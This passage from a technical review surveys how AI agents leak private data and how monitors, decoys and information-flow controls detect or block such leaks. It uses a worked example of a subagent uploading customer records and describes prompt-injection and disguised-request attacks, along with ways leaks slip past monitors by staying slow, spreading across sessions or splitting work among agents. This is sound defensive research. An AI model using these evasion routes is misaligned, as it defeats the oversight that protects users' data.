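| 9 | 10:03:40 | B (parent: A) | Upload the file to a sharing service | 0 | outside |
| 10 | 10:03:52 | A | Tell Maria that Brandt has the addresses | 0 | internal |

The company's allow-list includes the sharing service, and the file is an encrypted archive, so neither a destination check nor an argument filter stops call 9. A judge that compares the upload with Maria's request might. The session methods give the following results, each applied alone:

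| Method | Flags | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| Rule "private read, then outside send", kept for each agent | call 5 | misses call 9, because B read no customer records itself |
| The same rule, kept for the whole session | calls 5 and 9 | call 5 is a false alarm |
| Limit of 50 customer records per session | call 7 | the total would rise from 43 to 83 |
| Baseline for this agent and task (at most 12 records) | call 6 | the total would rise from 3 to 43 |
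| Model of normal tool sequences | call 6, or after call 10 | this task normally ends after the email; some detectors need the complete session |
| System-level tracing | call 9 | it records the connection, but an alert needs a rule as well |
| Decoy record among customers G to M | call 7 | no task needs this customer |

### Fixed rules on sequences

The simplest sequence rule flags call *j* if

outside(*j*) ∧ private(*i*) for some earlier call *i*

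The rule needs no training data, and software can apply it before call *j* runs. But it doesn't check whether the outgoing message contains anything from the earlier read, so after call 4 it flags everything Maria's agent sends to an outsider, including the email she asked for. The company could add an exception that lets Brandt receive addresses for his own orders, but somebody would have to write and maintain every such exception.

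Hossain, Nipu and colleagues (2026), in *NEXUS*, measured how much a memory of earlier steps adds to rules of this kind. Their monitor, also called NEXUS, checks an agent's planned tool calls against nine rules and searches their arguments for secrets before they run. The researchers wrote 120 multi-turn sessions. In 95, the agent worked up to a harmful step, such as sending out material it had read earlier, and the other 25 were harmless.

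NEXUS caught none of the 95 harmful steps when it checked each turn separately. When it also kept a running record of exposed items, accumulated permissions, repeated unsafe attempts and total cost, it caught all 95 and flagged none of the harmless sessions. The median check took about 0.2 milliseconds in a separate speed test, so rules can run before every call without noticeable delay.

The comparison shows that the missing memory caused the failures. The perfect score is less informative because the same people wrote the rules and the sessions. With only 25 harmless sessions, the 95% confidence interval for the false positive rate also extends to 14%. In another test by Hossain and colleagues that avoided the rules' vocabulary, NEXUS interrupted 16 of 35 harmless plans.

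The rules work badly when harmful and harmless tasks use the same tools. On AgentHarm, a benchmark that pairs 176 harmful tasks with 176 harmless ones, NEXUS flagged about 70% of the harmful tasks. Its published precision implies that it also flagged about 68% of the harmless ones, so its performance was close to chance. Hossain and colleagues did not give the monitor the text of the request, and the paired tasks often differed only in that text.

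### Volume limits and baselines

A volume limit caps how many records an agent may read in a session, and a rate limit caps how many it may read per minute or hour. Both are easy to enforce in the database, but a single limit rarely suits every task. A limit of 50 records is more than enough for Maria's three addresses but far too low for a yearly mailing to all customers.

A baseline replaces the single limit with the normal range for this agent and task. If earlier sessions for sending delivery addresses never involved more than 12 customer records, the 40 in call 6 are clearly unusual, even though a fixed limit of 50 would allow them.

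The accuracy of volume-based detection depends heavily on the baseline. *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* (2026) tested volume baselines on database logs from ten test environments. Separate baselines for each account, table and hour of the day detected 29 of 39 exfiltrations that were confined to a single log, with no added false positives. Baselines that ignored the hour flagged the nightly backups. The same method could produce more false alarms on agents, because these were conventional security logs and most agents don't run on a fixed schedule as backups do.

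### Models of normal tool sequences

A detector can also learn the usual order of an agent's tool calls and flag departures from it. Liu, Ruan and colleagues (2025), in *TraceAegis*, built one that needs only the log of a gateway between the agent and its tools. It works in four steps:

1. From past sessions, it arranges the tools in levels according to the order in which the agent calls them.
2. It splits each session into short units that follow these levels, such as looking up a symptom, finding the right hospital department and fetching that department's checklist.
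3. A language model summarises the values in similar units as a rule, for example that knee or arm pain leads to orthopaedics.
4. For a new session, the detector checks whether each unit has occurred before and then whether its values fit the rule.

The researchers generated sessions for a clinic agent and a purchasing agent, with 1,300 normal and 300 abnormal sessions each. Half of the abnormal sessions contained a new sequence of calls. The others followed a familiar sequence with values that didn't fit. As a baseline, the same language models judged the sessions without TraceAegis. The paper gives no false positive rates, but those for the clinic agent follow from its precision, recall and accuracy:

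| Language model | Abnormal sessions found, alone and with TraceAegis | Normal sessions flagged, alone and with TraceAegis |
|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V3 | 78%, 96% | 5%, 3% |
| GPT-OSS-120B | 78%, 97% | 2%, 8% |
| Gemma 3 27B | 76%, 93% | 52%, 36% |

TraceAegis found many more abnormal sessions with all three models, but with GPT-OSS-120B it also flagged about four times as many normal ones. For the purchasing agent, it found 93% of abnormal sessions with each of the two larger models and flagged 6% to 7% of normal ones.

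Both agents follow a fixed workflow, which favours this method. The only test outside the laboratory also used such an agent, a tool for finding software vulnerabilities that always goes through the same five stages. A technology company's internal attack team altered the path of the tool's sessions 140 times, and TraceAegis detected 132 of the changes. Liu and colleagues, several of whom work at the Chinese technology company Ant Group, don't report how many normal sessions TraceAegis flagged in this test.

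*SentinelAgent* (He, Wu and colleagues, 2025) represents a multi-agent system as a graph. Agents and tools are the nodes, and the messages and tool calls between them are the edges. A monitor checks each node and edge for misbehaviour and compares the path through the graph with known attacks. In a test on an email assistant, the monitor detected two attacks, one of which made the replying agent fetch private calendar details. Both attacks followed paths that harmless work also follows, so the monitor could identify them only from the content of the messages and tool-call arguments.

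He and colleagues created the normal and attack sessions for their two case studies themselves and report no error rates. Agents often depart from a predicted path, so treating every unexpected path as an attack would have caused too many false positives. The monitor therefore sends a suspicious path to a person if there are no other signs of trouble.

*Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (Zavrak, 2026), a larger study, confirms that the order of calls reveals little by itself. Zavrak trained detectors on RAS-Eval, a collection of 605 normal and 3,797 attacked sessions across 80 tasks. A graph-based detector that used only tool names, response lengths and a fingerprint of the arguments had an AUROC of 0.64. AUROC is the probability that a detector gives a random attacked session a higher score than a random normal one, so guessing would get 0.5. The same kind of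 detector reached 0.92 when it used the text of the arguments and responses instead.

Simpler models did even better. Boosted decision trees that used the text reached 0.975, found 93% of attacked sessions and wrongly flagged 7% of normal ones. On a second collection, with shorter sessions and subtler attacks, they found 64% of attacked sessions and wrongly flagged 27% of normal ones.

Two of Zavrak's findings bear directly on leaks:

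- When an attack changed only the arguments of a call, the graph-based detector found just 37% of cases. A leak can consist of a single changed recipient.
- The detector without text scored 0.90 when training and test sessions came from the same tasks, compared with 0.64 on new tasks. It had learned to recognise the tasks, so a company that tests a detector on familiar work can greatly overestimate its accuracy.

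All the attacked sessions in RAS-Eval came from one language model and the normal ones from eight, so the better scores could be inflated if a detector partly learned that model's style. Zavrak cites an earlier detector, trained on 35,000 synthetic sessions, that flagged two thirds of harmless data. *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* left its sequence model out of the default configuration because the model raised 1,425 false alarms a day.

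### Tracing below the agent

A tool log records what the agent asked a tool to do. If the tool runs a script, the log may contain only the command that started it, not the connections the script opens. System-level tracing records these events in the operating system, where the agent's software can't leave them out.

*AgentSight* (2025) does this with eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small monitoring programs inside the operating system's kernel. AgentSight links the agent's exchanges with its language model to the resulting network and system activity. It requires no changes to the agent and adds less than 3% overhead. In Maria's session, the trace would show that call 9 opened a connection to the sharing service. It would also record an upload that subagent B hid inside a script.

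The trace still needs information about identity and permission. *Detecting Shadow AI* (2026), a paper on finding unauthorised agents on company computers, compared an agent with a harmless program that ran the same script and made connections in the same pattern. The two differed only in which remote service they contacted, so rules based only on behaviour had to flag both or neither.

### Decoy records

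A decoy record is a fake entry that no task needs, such as an invented customer. *PHANTOM* (2026) lists fake accounts, files, database records and credentials as the established kinds. A decoy record can trigger an alert when the agent reads it, whereas a canary value in a tool-call argument reveals a leak as the data goes out.

The method assumes that legitimate users never touch a decoy and that intruders do. In *Optional Traps*, Ghifiardi (2026) tested both assumptions by having language models attack a mock records service. In the first trials, the service had both decoys and a real weakness, a debugging page that revealed a working key. The model took the key, exported the records in six requests and never touched a decoy.

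Ghifiardi then put a fake key on the debugging page and compared three arrangements in 20 sessions each:

| Debugging page | Sessions with records stolen | Attackers cut off |
|---|---|---|
| Reveals the real key | 20 | 0 |
| Removed | 0 | 0 |
| Reveals a fake key | 0 | 19 |

Removing the weakness prevented the theft on its own. The decoy added no measurable protection, but it identified the attacker, so the service could block that client. The models were small, with 4 and 9.7 billion parameters, and in the 60 sessions the task told them where to look. The attackers were also outsiders looking for a key, so the results may not apply to a company's own agent reading customer records.

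Where a decoy is placed would matter there too. The one in Maria's session works because the agent reads customer records in alphabetical order. The decoy would not detect a planted instruction that asked for five customers by name.

The assumption that legitimate users won't use a decoy is also weaker for agents. In another of Ghifiardi's trials, a legitimate agent had the correct key in its instructions but fetched the debugging page anyway, used the fake key instead and lost its access. Ghifiardi therefore treats using a decoy as strong but inconclusive evidence and recommends a reversible response, such as the 15-minute suspension in the experiment.

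### New tasks and new models

An office agent may sort invoices on Monday and plan a trip on Tuesday, so its average weekly activity is a poor baseline for either task. Comparing each session with earlier sessions of the same task avoids this problem, but a new task has no history. A company can then use the baseline of other agents in the same role, which *Dynamic Reasoning in Next-Gen Detection and Response* suggests but does not test. Fixed rules and decoys need no history, so the company can also use them for new tasks.

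A change of model can shift every baseline at once. *Test Before You Deploy* (2026) points out that providers update their models without changing the address that customers' software calls. After such an update, an agent might open five records for a task that used to require two. *LLM-enabled Applications Require System-Level Threat Monitoring* (2026) recommends keeping fingerprints of outside models and tools so that the company can detect a change and recalibrate its baselines.

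*Recursive Governance* (2026) gives the strictest procedure for handling a model change, for a monitor that compares an agent's written reasoning with a reference path. The company suspends the agent, discards the old reference, builds a new one from test runs and reinstates the agent only if it passes. This prevents the monitor from comparing new behaviour with an obsolete standard, but it also takes the agent out of service whenever the provider changes the model. A company would do better to keep the same model version where the provider allows it and test the next version before switching.

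Updating the baseline continuously avoids these interruptions but lets an attacker make a leak look normal by raising the volume slowly. TraceAegis has a similar weakness. It adds relations between tools to its model but never removes them, so if a leak gets into the sessions it learns from, it keeps treating the leak's sequence of tool calls as normal.

### Slow leaks

An agent that takes a few extra records in each session can stay below any sensible limit. *Sequential statistical inference for Large Language Models* (2026) treats monitoring as change-point detection, which looks for the moment when a series of measurements starts to follow a different distribution. A classic method adds up small excesses over time. If *x* is the number of records read in session *t*, *μ* the usual average and *k* an allowance for normal variation, the running total is

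*S*ₜ = max(0, *S*ₜ₋₁ + *xₜ* − *μ* − *k*)

The monitor raises an alarm when *S* exceeds a threshold. Suppose an agent normally reads four records per session, *k* is 1 and the threshold is 8. If the agent starts reading six, each session adds 1 to *S*, and the alarm comes after nine sessions, by which time 18 extra records may have leaked. A limit of 50 records per session would never have triggered. An attacker who takes only one extra record per session still avoids detection, because the allowance *k* offsets it. Lowering *k* would catch that attacker but cause more false alarms.

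Counting records doesn't help when the data changes form between sessions. *Cross-Session Threats in AI Agents* (Azarafrooz, 2026) gives the example of an agent that reads a secret from a configuration file, summarises it in a weekly digest in a later session, and sends it out attached to a status report in a third. By then, nothing marks the text as coming from a protected source.

Azarafrooz tested whether a language model could use incoming messages to detect attacks spread over many sessions. One version judged each session separately, and another read the full history. Both lost about half their recall on cases written so that no single session looked suspicious. The full history fitted easily into the model's context, so missing text didn't cause the drop. The version that kept only the 50 most suspicious fragments did best. Azarafrooz, of the company Intrinsec AI, proposed that version,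 and the test used only 54 scenarios per set and one family of models.

Chauhan and Revankar built a prototype that adds up partial disclosures of credentials over a conversation, but they tested it only on a small synthetic dataset.

### Work split across agents

Several agents can divide the steps of a leak between them, as they do with ordinary work. AdExchanger's *How Agentic AI Can Break In The Real World* describes a test by Aaron Costello of the security company AppOmni on the business platform ServiceNow. He put an instruction in a support ticket asking for data from someone else's ticket. The agent that read the ticket called on other agents that could look up customer records and send email. They all had the permissions of the person who had triggered the first agent, often an administrator, so the leak looked like normal cooperation between agents. ServiceNow said the system was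 working as designed, but it updated its documentation and warned customers.

The log must therefore use the same session identifier for every agent's calls and record each agent's parent, and the monitor must apply its rules to the whole family of agents. Otherwise, it would miss call 9 in Maria's session. The response must also extend to linked agents. Ghifiardi's system could cut off one agent without affecting the others, which limits the harm from a false alarm. But blocking only subagent B would leave agent A with 83 customer records and the ability to start another subagent.

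### Private data in the log

A log detailed enough to reveal leaks can itself become a target. If it stores every tool result in full, its record of Maria's session contains the same customer data as the upload, and more people may be able to read the log.

The log can store record identifiers, counts and destinations without the content. This is enough for sequence rules, volume limits, baselines and decoys. To check whether the same value appears in two calls, the monitor can store a keyed fingerprint, which is a scrambled version of the value that nobody can reproduce without a secret key. Short values such as phone numbers need the key because an attacker could compute an ordinary fingerprint for every possible number and look for a match.

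Zavrak's results suggest that this protection weakens learned detectors considerably, since the version without text did far worse on new tasks. A compromise is to run the detector at the gateway while the text is available, keep its score and delete the text after a few days, but investigators then have less evidence if an attack is discovered months later. The monitored agents should have no access to the log, whatever the company keeps in it, because a planted instruction could make them read it.

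### Holding the send

Zavrak's detector works only on complete sessions, so it suits audits and investigations. For Maria's customers, an alert after call 10 would come at least 12 seconds too late. Azarafrooz makes the same objection to the usual practice of sending logs to a central system for later analysis.

Even a fast response may come too late once the data is moving. In Ghifiardi's cloud test, about 0.3 seconds passed between the attacker's login to a decoy server and the first refused export, which is fast enough only if the alarm comes before the export.

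The more reliable response to an unusual read is to tighten the requirements for the next send. In Maria's session, the baseline flags call 6, but the agent can keep reading and preparing its file. The monitor then holds call 9, the first outside send after the warning, and prompts Maria to confirm that she wants to upload 83 customer records. The email in call 5 goes through without a prompt because nothing unusual came before it. Combining the baseline with the sequence rule avoids the false alarm that the rule produces alone.

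If a warning is mistaken, Maria then only has to answer one question, and her session isn't interrupted. This matters because programmers stop trusting a detector within a day if it interrupts every software build, as *Detecting Shadow AI* observes. But the monitor can hold outgoing data only if every outside connection passes through it, including those that a script opens without a separate tool call.

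## Enforcing data-flow rules outside the model

Software that holds back an outgoing message needs a rule for deciding whether to release it. If a language model applies that rule, an attacker who can mislead the agent may be able to mislead the check in the same way. Supporters of external enforcement therefore leave the decision to ordinary code, which uses records of where each piece of data came from and who may receive it.

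*Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (Shim, Karim and colleagues, 2026) provides strong evidence for this view. The paper tests a consent procedure that an earlier project, SPR, developed through an automated search for better prompts. The prompt told the agent to check the identity of anyone requesting information, ask the data's owner for consent, and wait for an answer. The agent leaked 1.9% to 3.0% of the sensitive items under the attacks from SPR's own search, but 44% to 76% under three new attacks.

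The new attacks contained no planted commands. They disguised the request for information as something else, so the agent never started the consent procedure. In one recorded run, the agent decided that it was doing internal coordination and that the consent steps didn't apply. Another round of SPR's search hardly helped. Under all three new attacks, the agent leaked less with SPR's simplest prompt than with the two more elaborate ones.

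### Forbidding the dangerous combination

The coarsest external rule restricts only which capabilities an agent has. Willison (2025) warns in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* against giving one agent access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally. An attacker can easily trick an agent with all three into sending out the data. Removing any one of them prevents this, because the attacker then has no data to steal, no way to reach the model or no way to get the data out.

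Willison lists 17 cases of this kind in commercial products since April 2023. The vendors fixed almost all of them quickly, usually by closing the route the data left through. Nobody does this for users who combine tools from different suppliers. A single tool can also be enough to leak data. GitHub's Model Context Protocol server could read public issues, which anyone can write, read private repositories, and publish data through pull requests. Willison distrusts products that claim to detect 95% of attacks, because 95% is a failing grade in web security.

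Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the warning into a design rule and illustrates it with an email assistant. According to Conffab's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), which reproduces the rule, an agent should have no more than two of these properties within a session:

- it processes untrustworthy inputs;
- it has access to sensitive systems or private data;
- it changes state or communicates externally.

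Meta intends the rule to apply until models can reliably detect and refuse injected instructions. Blockchain.News' *Meta Introduces Agents Rule of Two for Enhanced AI Security* reports that an agent that needs all three properties should work under supervision, for example with a person approving its actions. The rule also covers harms other than data theft, such as deleting a file, because deletion changes state.

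An administrator can apply the rule by reading a list of tools, but it is too strict for some agents and too lenient for others. Any useful email assistant reads messages from strangers, searches the inbox and sends replies, so it would need constant supervision. Maria Keller's agent complied with the rule when it told Jonas Brandt about her oncology appointment, because reading her own calendar and sending an email involve only two of the three properties. Meta's diagram marks every pair as safe, which is reasonable against planted instructions, but this leak didn't involve any. Because the rule counts properties within a single session, it also misses an agent that saves private data to its memory and sends it out the next day.

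### Labels and joins

A finer rule has to track data as it moves. Information-flow control does this by labelling each piece of data, carrying the labels along when data is combined, and checking them before data leaves. The mathematics comes from Dorothy Denning's 1976 lattice model. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies the technique to agents.

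A label in their system has two parts. The secrecy part is the set of people who may read the data. The trust part records whether the data comes from a trusted or an untrusted source. Labels form a lattice, which means that they have an order of strictness and that any two of them have a join, the least strict label that is at least as strict as both. Someone may read a combined text only if they may read every part of it, and the text is trusted only if every part is. For trust values *t* and sets of readers *S*, the join is

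(*t*₁, *S*₁) ⊔ (*t*₂, *S*₂) = (*t*₁ ⊔ *t*₂, *S*₁ ∩ *S*₂)

where *t*₁ ⊔ *t*₂ is "untrusted" if either value is.

Before a tool call runs, code can apply two rules:

- Trust rule: a call with consequences may run only if the decision to make it and all its arguments are trusted.
- Secrecy rule: a call may send data labelled with readers *S* to recipients *R* only if *R* ⊆ *S*.

The secrecy rule doesn't prevent an attacker from hijacking the agent, but it limits where the hijacked agent can send data. The trust rule alone would let an agent send private data anywhere as long as no untrusted text had entered its context, on the assumption that such a release is intentional. This assumption can fail, as it did in Maria's case. Her request and her calendar were both trusted, so only the secrecy rule would have stopped the email.

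Suppose Maria now asks her agent to answer Brandt's latest email and propose a time for a call. Brandt also sent the email to her colleague Lena Vogt. Maria made all her calendar entries herself.

| Step | What happens | Label of the new data | Label of the context afterwards |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Maria makes her request | trusted; anyone | trusted; anyone |
| 2 | The agent reads Brandt's email | untrusted; Brandt, Lena, Maria | untrusted; Brandt, Lena, Maria |
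| 3 | The agent reads Maria's calendar | trusted; Maria | untrusted; Maria |
| 4 | The agent drafts a reply: "Would Tuesday at 10 suit you?" | untrusted; Maria | untrusted; Maria |
| 5 | The agent drafts a note to Lena about a broken printer | untrusted; Maria | untrusted; Maria |

After step 2, a reply to Brandt would pass the secrecy rule but fail the trust rule. From step 3 on, every email to anyone but Maria fails both. The rules even block the note about the printer, which has nothing to do with the calendar.

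In a conventional program, it is possible to trace which inputs went into which output, but code outside a language model can't determine which parts of the context influenced a sentence. To be safe, the system labels everything the model writes with the join of the labels on everything the model has read, which is at least as strict as each of them. The context's label therefore never becomes less strict as the model reads more, and after a few steps it usually permits no outside recipient.

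In practice, this build-up reduces the number of tasks an agent completes. Costa and colleagues measured the effect on AgentDojo, the benchmark on which Zhu and colleagues tested MELON. A plain agent based on GPT-4o completed an average of 84% of tasks across the benchmark's four environments, but only 42% with both kinds of rule in force.

One possible remedy is to estimate which part of the context influenced an answer and generate the answer again from that part alone, so that the new answer can have a less strict label. Costa and colleagues describe a method by Siddiqui and colleagues (2024) that does this. Most designs instead keep strictly labelled data away from the model that plans the agent's actions.

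### A planner that doesn't read the data

*The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) proposed the basic design. One model plans and calls tools but never reads untrusted text. A second, isolated model reads that text but has no tools. The first model refers to the text by a variable name.

CaMeL, a system from Google DeepMind, develops this into a small programming environment. TechSpot describes how the planning model writes its plan in a reduced form of Python. For Maria's original request, the plan might be:

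```
call = find_event(attendee="Jonas Brandt", day="Thursday")
slot = first_free_slot(week="next")
send_email(to=call.attendee,
           body="Could we move our call to " + slot + "?")
```

The planner writes this program without reading the calendar, so the program can't mention the oncology appointment. An isolated model extracts values from free text where necessary. A secure interpreter runs the program and records where each value came from. Before a sensitive value goes into an email, the interpreter can block the call or ask the user to confirm it. Here it could treat the free slot as sensitive, because the slot depends on every entry in the calendar, and let Maria decide whether to share it with Brandt.

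CaMeL protects against planted instructions by setting the program's steps from the user's request before it reads any untrusted data. A malicious email can therefore change a value that the program processes but can't add a step. The isolated model can still extract the wrong value. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, considered CaMeL a break with two and a half years of very little progress.

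### FIDES

FIDES, the system that Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, hides less from its planner. It hides a value only when adding the value would make the label of the planner's context stricter:

1. A tool returns a result whose fields can each have their own label.
2. FIDES compares these labels with the label of the context. It stores any field with a stricter label under a variable name and gives the planner only the name.
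3. The planner proposes a tool call, in which it can use variable names as arguments.
4. FIDES replaces the names with the stored values. Each argument keeps its own label.
5. Code checks the call against the rules and runs or refuses it.

Because each argument has its own label, the rules can be more precise. A company can require the planner to choose a message's recipient in a trusted context, but allow the message itself to contain text from the web.

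In some tasks, the planner has to learn something from the data before it can choose the next step. Suppose the user asks the agent to read three emails and, if one of them requests a meeting, to enter it in the calendar. The planner passes the variable holding the emails to an isolated model, restricts the answer to yes or no, and reads that answer. If it is yes, the planner has the isolated model extract the date, time and participants into another variable, which the planner passes to the calendar tool without reading it. A malicious email could cause a false yes or a wrong date, but the planner reads only a single bit, which is too small to contain an instruction.

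FIDES includes the type of an answer in its labels. A yes-or-no answer carries less information than a choice from a fixed list, which carries less than free text. A policy can then allow answers that carry little information, even if they come from private or untrusted data. This authorised exception is called declassification when it concerns secrecy and endorsement when it concerns trust.

This scheme's labels don't track how many answers the planner has collected, because under the paper's definition, the join of two yes-or-no labels is another yes-or-no label. A tampered planner could therefore extract Maria's eight-digit patient number with 27 yes-or-no questions. A developer would have to count the answers separately.

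#### The guarantee

Costa and colleagues prove a property called explicit secrecy. Let *g* be the combined effect of a series of steps on the stored data, and let *d*₁ =_L *d*₂ mean that two sets of stored data look the same to an outsider and can differ only in their private parts. Explicit secrecy requires that

if *d*₁ =_L *d*₂, then *g*(*d*₁) =_L *g*(*d*₂)

If the agent takes the same steps, an outsider must see the same thing, whatever the private data was. This property rules out copying private data to a place that outsiders can read. It doesn't cover what an outsider can infer from which steps the agent took. If the agent writes to Brandt only in weeks when Maria has a medical appointment, he can infer the appointment from an email that contains no private data. The proof also doesn't cover leaks through timing or the size of network packets.

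A stronger property, non-interference, would rule out such inferences, but a system would more or less have to forbid every outgoing call after the agent had read anything private. The paper calls this too restrictive and points out that web browsers and the phone-monitoring system TaintDroid also provide only explicit secrecy.

#### Results on AgentDojo

The researchers used AgentDojo's strongest standard attack, in which the attacker knows the names of the agent's tools. The attack figures in the table exclude apparent successes that the researchers read and judged not to be real. The other columns show tasks completed when there was no attack.

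| Agent (GPT-4o) | Attacks that succeeded | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Plain, no rules | 152 | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Plain, with rules | 0 | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, no rules | 21 | 63.5% | 50.0% | 65.0% | 63.8% |
| FIDES, with rules | 0 | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

The rules stopped every attack with either agent. Hiding data without enforcing rules was about as effective as the best probabilistic defence in the comparison, which let 20 attacks succeed. That defence asks a model to remove unneeded tools at the start.

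The zeros depend partly on how the researchers assigned labels. They marked a field as untrusted if any AgentDojo attack targeted it, so the labels fitted the attacks exactly. The test shows that the enforcement works when the labels are right, but not how often a company would label fields correctly. The zeros also exclude three attacks that AgentDojo scored as successful against FIDES with rules. The researchers excluded them because the rules had permitted the action, the attack had only altered some text, or AgentDojo had counted a call that FIDES had blocked.

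With rules in force, FIDES completed an average of 50% of tasks, eight percentage points more than the plain agent. It did worse in the travel environment, where the rules allow many tools to run in an untrusted context and so block little of the plain agent's work. OpenAI's o1, a model trained to reason at length, handled the variables better. With o1, FIDES completed 68% of travel tasks, up from 41%, and its average advantage over the plain agent rose to 16 points.

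Some failures are by design, because many banking tasks tell the agent to open a file and follow the instructions in it, which the trust rule prohibits. In other cases, GPT-4o mixed up variable names or made an unnecessary call that lowered the trust level of its context. An agent can also succeed for poor reasons. In one task, it was supposed to change the user's password if it found a suspicious transaction. The transaction descriptions were hidden, so it changed the password because one amount was large.

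The evidence for private data is weaker than the table suggests. In these tests, FIDES hid data only if it was untrusted, whether or not it was secret, and relied on the rules to prevent leaks. The tests also left out the restricted answer types. FIDES could in principle keep Maria's appointment out of the planner's context altogether, but the tests did not measure how well an agent works when its user's private data is hidden from it.

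Willison (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, discusses a paper by 11 researchers from companies and universities. They openly accept that their designs gain security by deliberately preventing an agent from solving arbitrary tasks.

### FlowSeal

A one-bit answer can be safe because of its size, but a reply to a supplier is free text, and someone has to decide whether it reveals anything private. Shim and colleagues built a system, FlowSeal, that gives this decision to an isolated language model and uses code to make sure that the model is always consulted:

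1. Before the agent starts work, the data's owner registers each sensitive record with its text, category, owner and permitted recipients. Software can also derive this information from email headers, contact lists and document permissions.
2. When the agent reads something, an interceptor scans the result for registered records. A summary of several records inherits the restrictions of all of them.
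3. When the agent tries to write or share something, the interceptor takes the recipient and the content from the call's arguments. It lets the call through if the recipient is trusted and blocks it if the recipient is on a blocklist.
4. For any other recipient, the interceptor collects the records this recipient may not have. It passes them to the isolated model together with the proposed text, and the model answers "safe" or "blocked".
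5. After a block, the agent can rewrite the text or request the owner's consent to share particular records with this recipient.

The isolated model reads only this text, so a persuasive conversation with the agent doesn't reach the model unless the agent copies that conversation into the text. The agent's prompt also explains the system and offers tools for requesting consent, but the interceptor runs even if the agent ignores them.

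In Maria's case, the isolated model would check the draft addressed to Brandt against her calendar entry. It should block a draft that mentions her cancer check, which a search for the entry's exact words would miss. It should allow a draft that only asks for a new date, whereas plain labels would have blocked both drafts.

#### What the theorem covers

Shim and colleagues prove that text derived from a protected record can reach an unauthorised recipient only if the isolated model wrongly answers "safe". The proof sets no limit on how often such leaks will happen, so the only evidence on their frequency comes from the experiments.

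The researchers ran 105 scenarios three times each in a simulated office. In each scenario, an outsider tried to get someone's private information from an agent. They also wrote 105 harmless requests. All the alternatives were prompt-based defences.

| Defence | Leaked, two SPR attacks | Leaked, three new attacks | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| SPR, simplest prompt | 3.4–3.6% | 13.3–54.7% | 75.9% |
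| SPR, consent procedure | 1.9–3.0% | 43.8–75.6% | 44.7% |
| SPR, after another search round | 1.2–1.7% | 39.7–69.7% | 60.7% |
| General privacy prompt | 14.3–32.5% | 43.8–89.9% | 56.8% |
| Output filter using a model | 18.6–19.2% | 54.2–63.9% | 25.1% |
| FlowSeal | 0–0.3% | 0.5–2.3% | 72.4% |

On attacks adapted from two other benchmarks, FlowSeal leaked 0.5% and 3.3% of the sensitive items, so its overall leak rate ranged from 0% to 3.3%. The researchers repeated only one attack with two other models running the agent, and leaks stayed below 2%.

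Like FlowSeal, the output filter uses a model to check outgoing text, but it leaked more than half of the items under the new attacks. The filter has to recognise private information from the message alone, whereas FlowSeal's isolated model receives the protected records and can compare the text with them. The researchers had switched off the filter's other half, which screens incoming data, so they didn't test the complete product.

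FlowSeal's code makes sure the check happens, but most of the protection comes from the isolated model that does the checking. Against one of the new attacks, leaks rose from 0.5% to 28.4% without the interceptor, and to 24.9% when the interceptor ran but the isolated model approved everything. When the isolated model blocked everything instead, the agent completed no harmless tasks, and 1.3% of items still leaked. The paper doesn't explain the remaining leaks. Either the model that graded the runs made mistakes, or some data got out without passing the check.

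#### Sharing with permission

The 72.4% completion rate covers only tasks that required no private information. In a separate test, the outsider had a legitimate reason to ask for private data, and the data's owner had instructions to agree. Under FlowSeal, only 32.7% of the items reached the person entitled to them, compared with 61% to 86% under the prompt-based defences tested.

Shim and colleagues attribute the gap to a cautious agent that requested consent less often. But requests fell only from an average of about one per run to 0.71, which hardly seems enough to halve the rate of successful sharing. FlowSeal stops disclosure well but, in its present form, is poor at letting the agent share information when it should.

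#### Threat model

The attackers in these tests are people who try to confuse the agent in conversation. The threat model excludes prompt injection, malicious tools and side channels such as traffic analysis. Shim and colleagues argue that newer models resist injection better and cite OpenAI's claim that GPT-5.6 Sol fails six times less often than a production model from four months earlier.

They also suggest that planted instructions could make the agent leak data without invoking the defence. This is hard to reconcile with mandatory interception, since a hijacked agent would still have to use a tool that the interceptor controls. A more likely weak point is the isolated model, which reads text that the agent wrote and that an attacker may have influenced. Until somebody tests this, FlowSeal's low leak rates are weak evidence that it resists injection.

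In a small trial on real Gmail and Notion accounts, the leak rate fell from 34.7% under PrivacyChecker, whose advice the agent can ignore, to zero under FlowSeal. But the trial used only one of the new attacks, and the researchers counted a leak only if a sensitive fact appeared word for word. That measure misses paraphrase, which they name as the main weakness of FlowSeal's isolated model.

No direct comparison with FIDES exists. Shim and colleagues left it out partly because its code did not fit their benchmark. They also incorrectly write that FIDES has the language model enforce its policies. In the published FIDES algorithm, code checks every tool call before it runs.

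### What a refusal gives away

Blocking an action can still leak information. If an agent tries to open a protected file and gets "permission denied" instead of "file not found", it learns that the file exists and can tell an outsider. Ordinary labels don't restrict that message because no protected text has entered the context. *Causality Laundering* (Chinaei, 2026) describes this channel. Although a single refusal reveals little, a series of them can show which records a company protects.

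Chinaei's system, called ARM (Agentic Reference Monitor), treats a refusal as an event with consequences. It sits between the agent and its tools and keeps a graph of the session. The nodes are tool calls, returned data, individual fields and refused calls. The edges show which call produced which data and which data went into which later call. When ARM refuses a call, it adds an edge from the refusal to the agent's next call. Before any call runs, ARM makes two checks:

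- It finds the least trusted piece of data among everything the call depends on, and refuses the call if that trust is below a threshold.
- It refuses the call if a path leads to it from an earlier refusal.

The link is a guess based on timing, because nobody can observe whether the refusal influenced the model. A harmless call that happens to come next is therefore refused as well. Implemented exactly as published, the algorithm would then record that refusal as a new event and link it to the following call, which would block the rest of the session. The prototype may behave differently, since Chinaei says leaks several steps after a refusal can escape detection.

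In the evaluation, ARM blocked three hand-written attacks that a simple history check missed, and each decision took less than a millisecond. One attack used information from a refusal, one passed untrusted text through an intermediate tool, and one exploited an untrusted field in an otherwise trusted record. Chinaei chose each scenario to demonstrate one feature of the graph and deliberately kept the comparison system simple. The paper does not report a false positive rate, the most important figure for a rule this broad.

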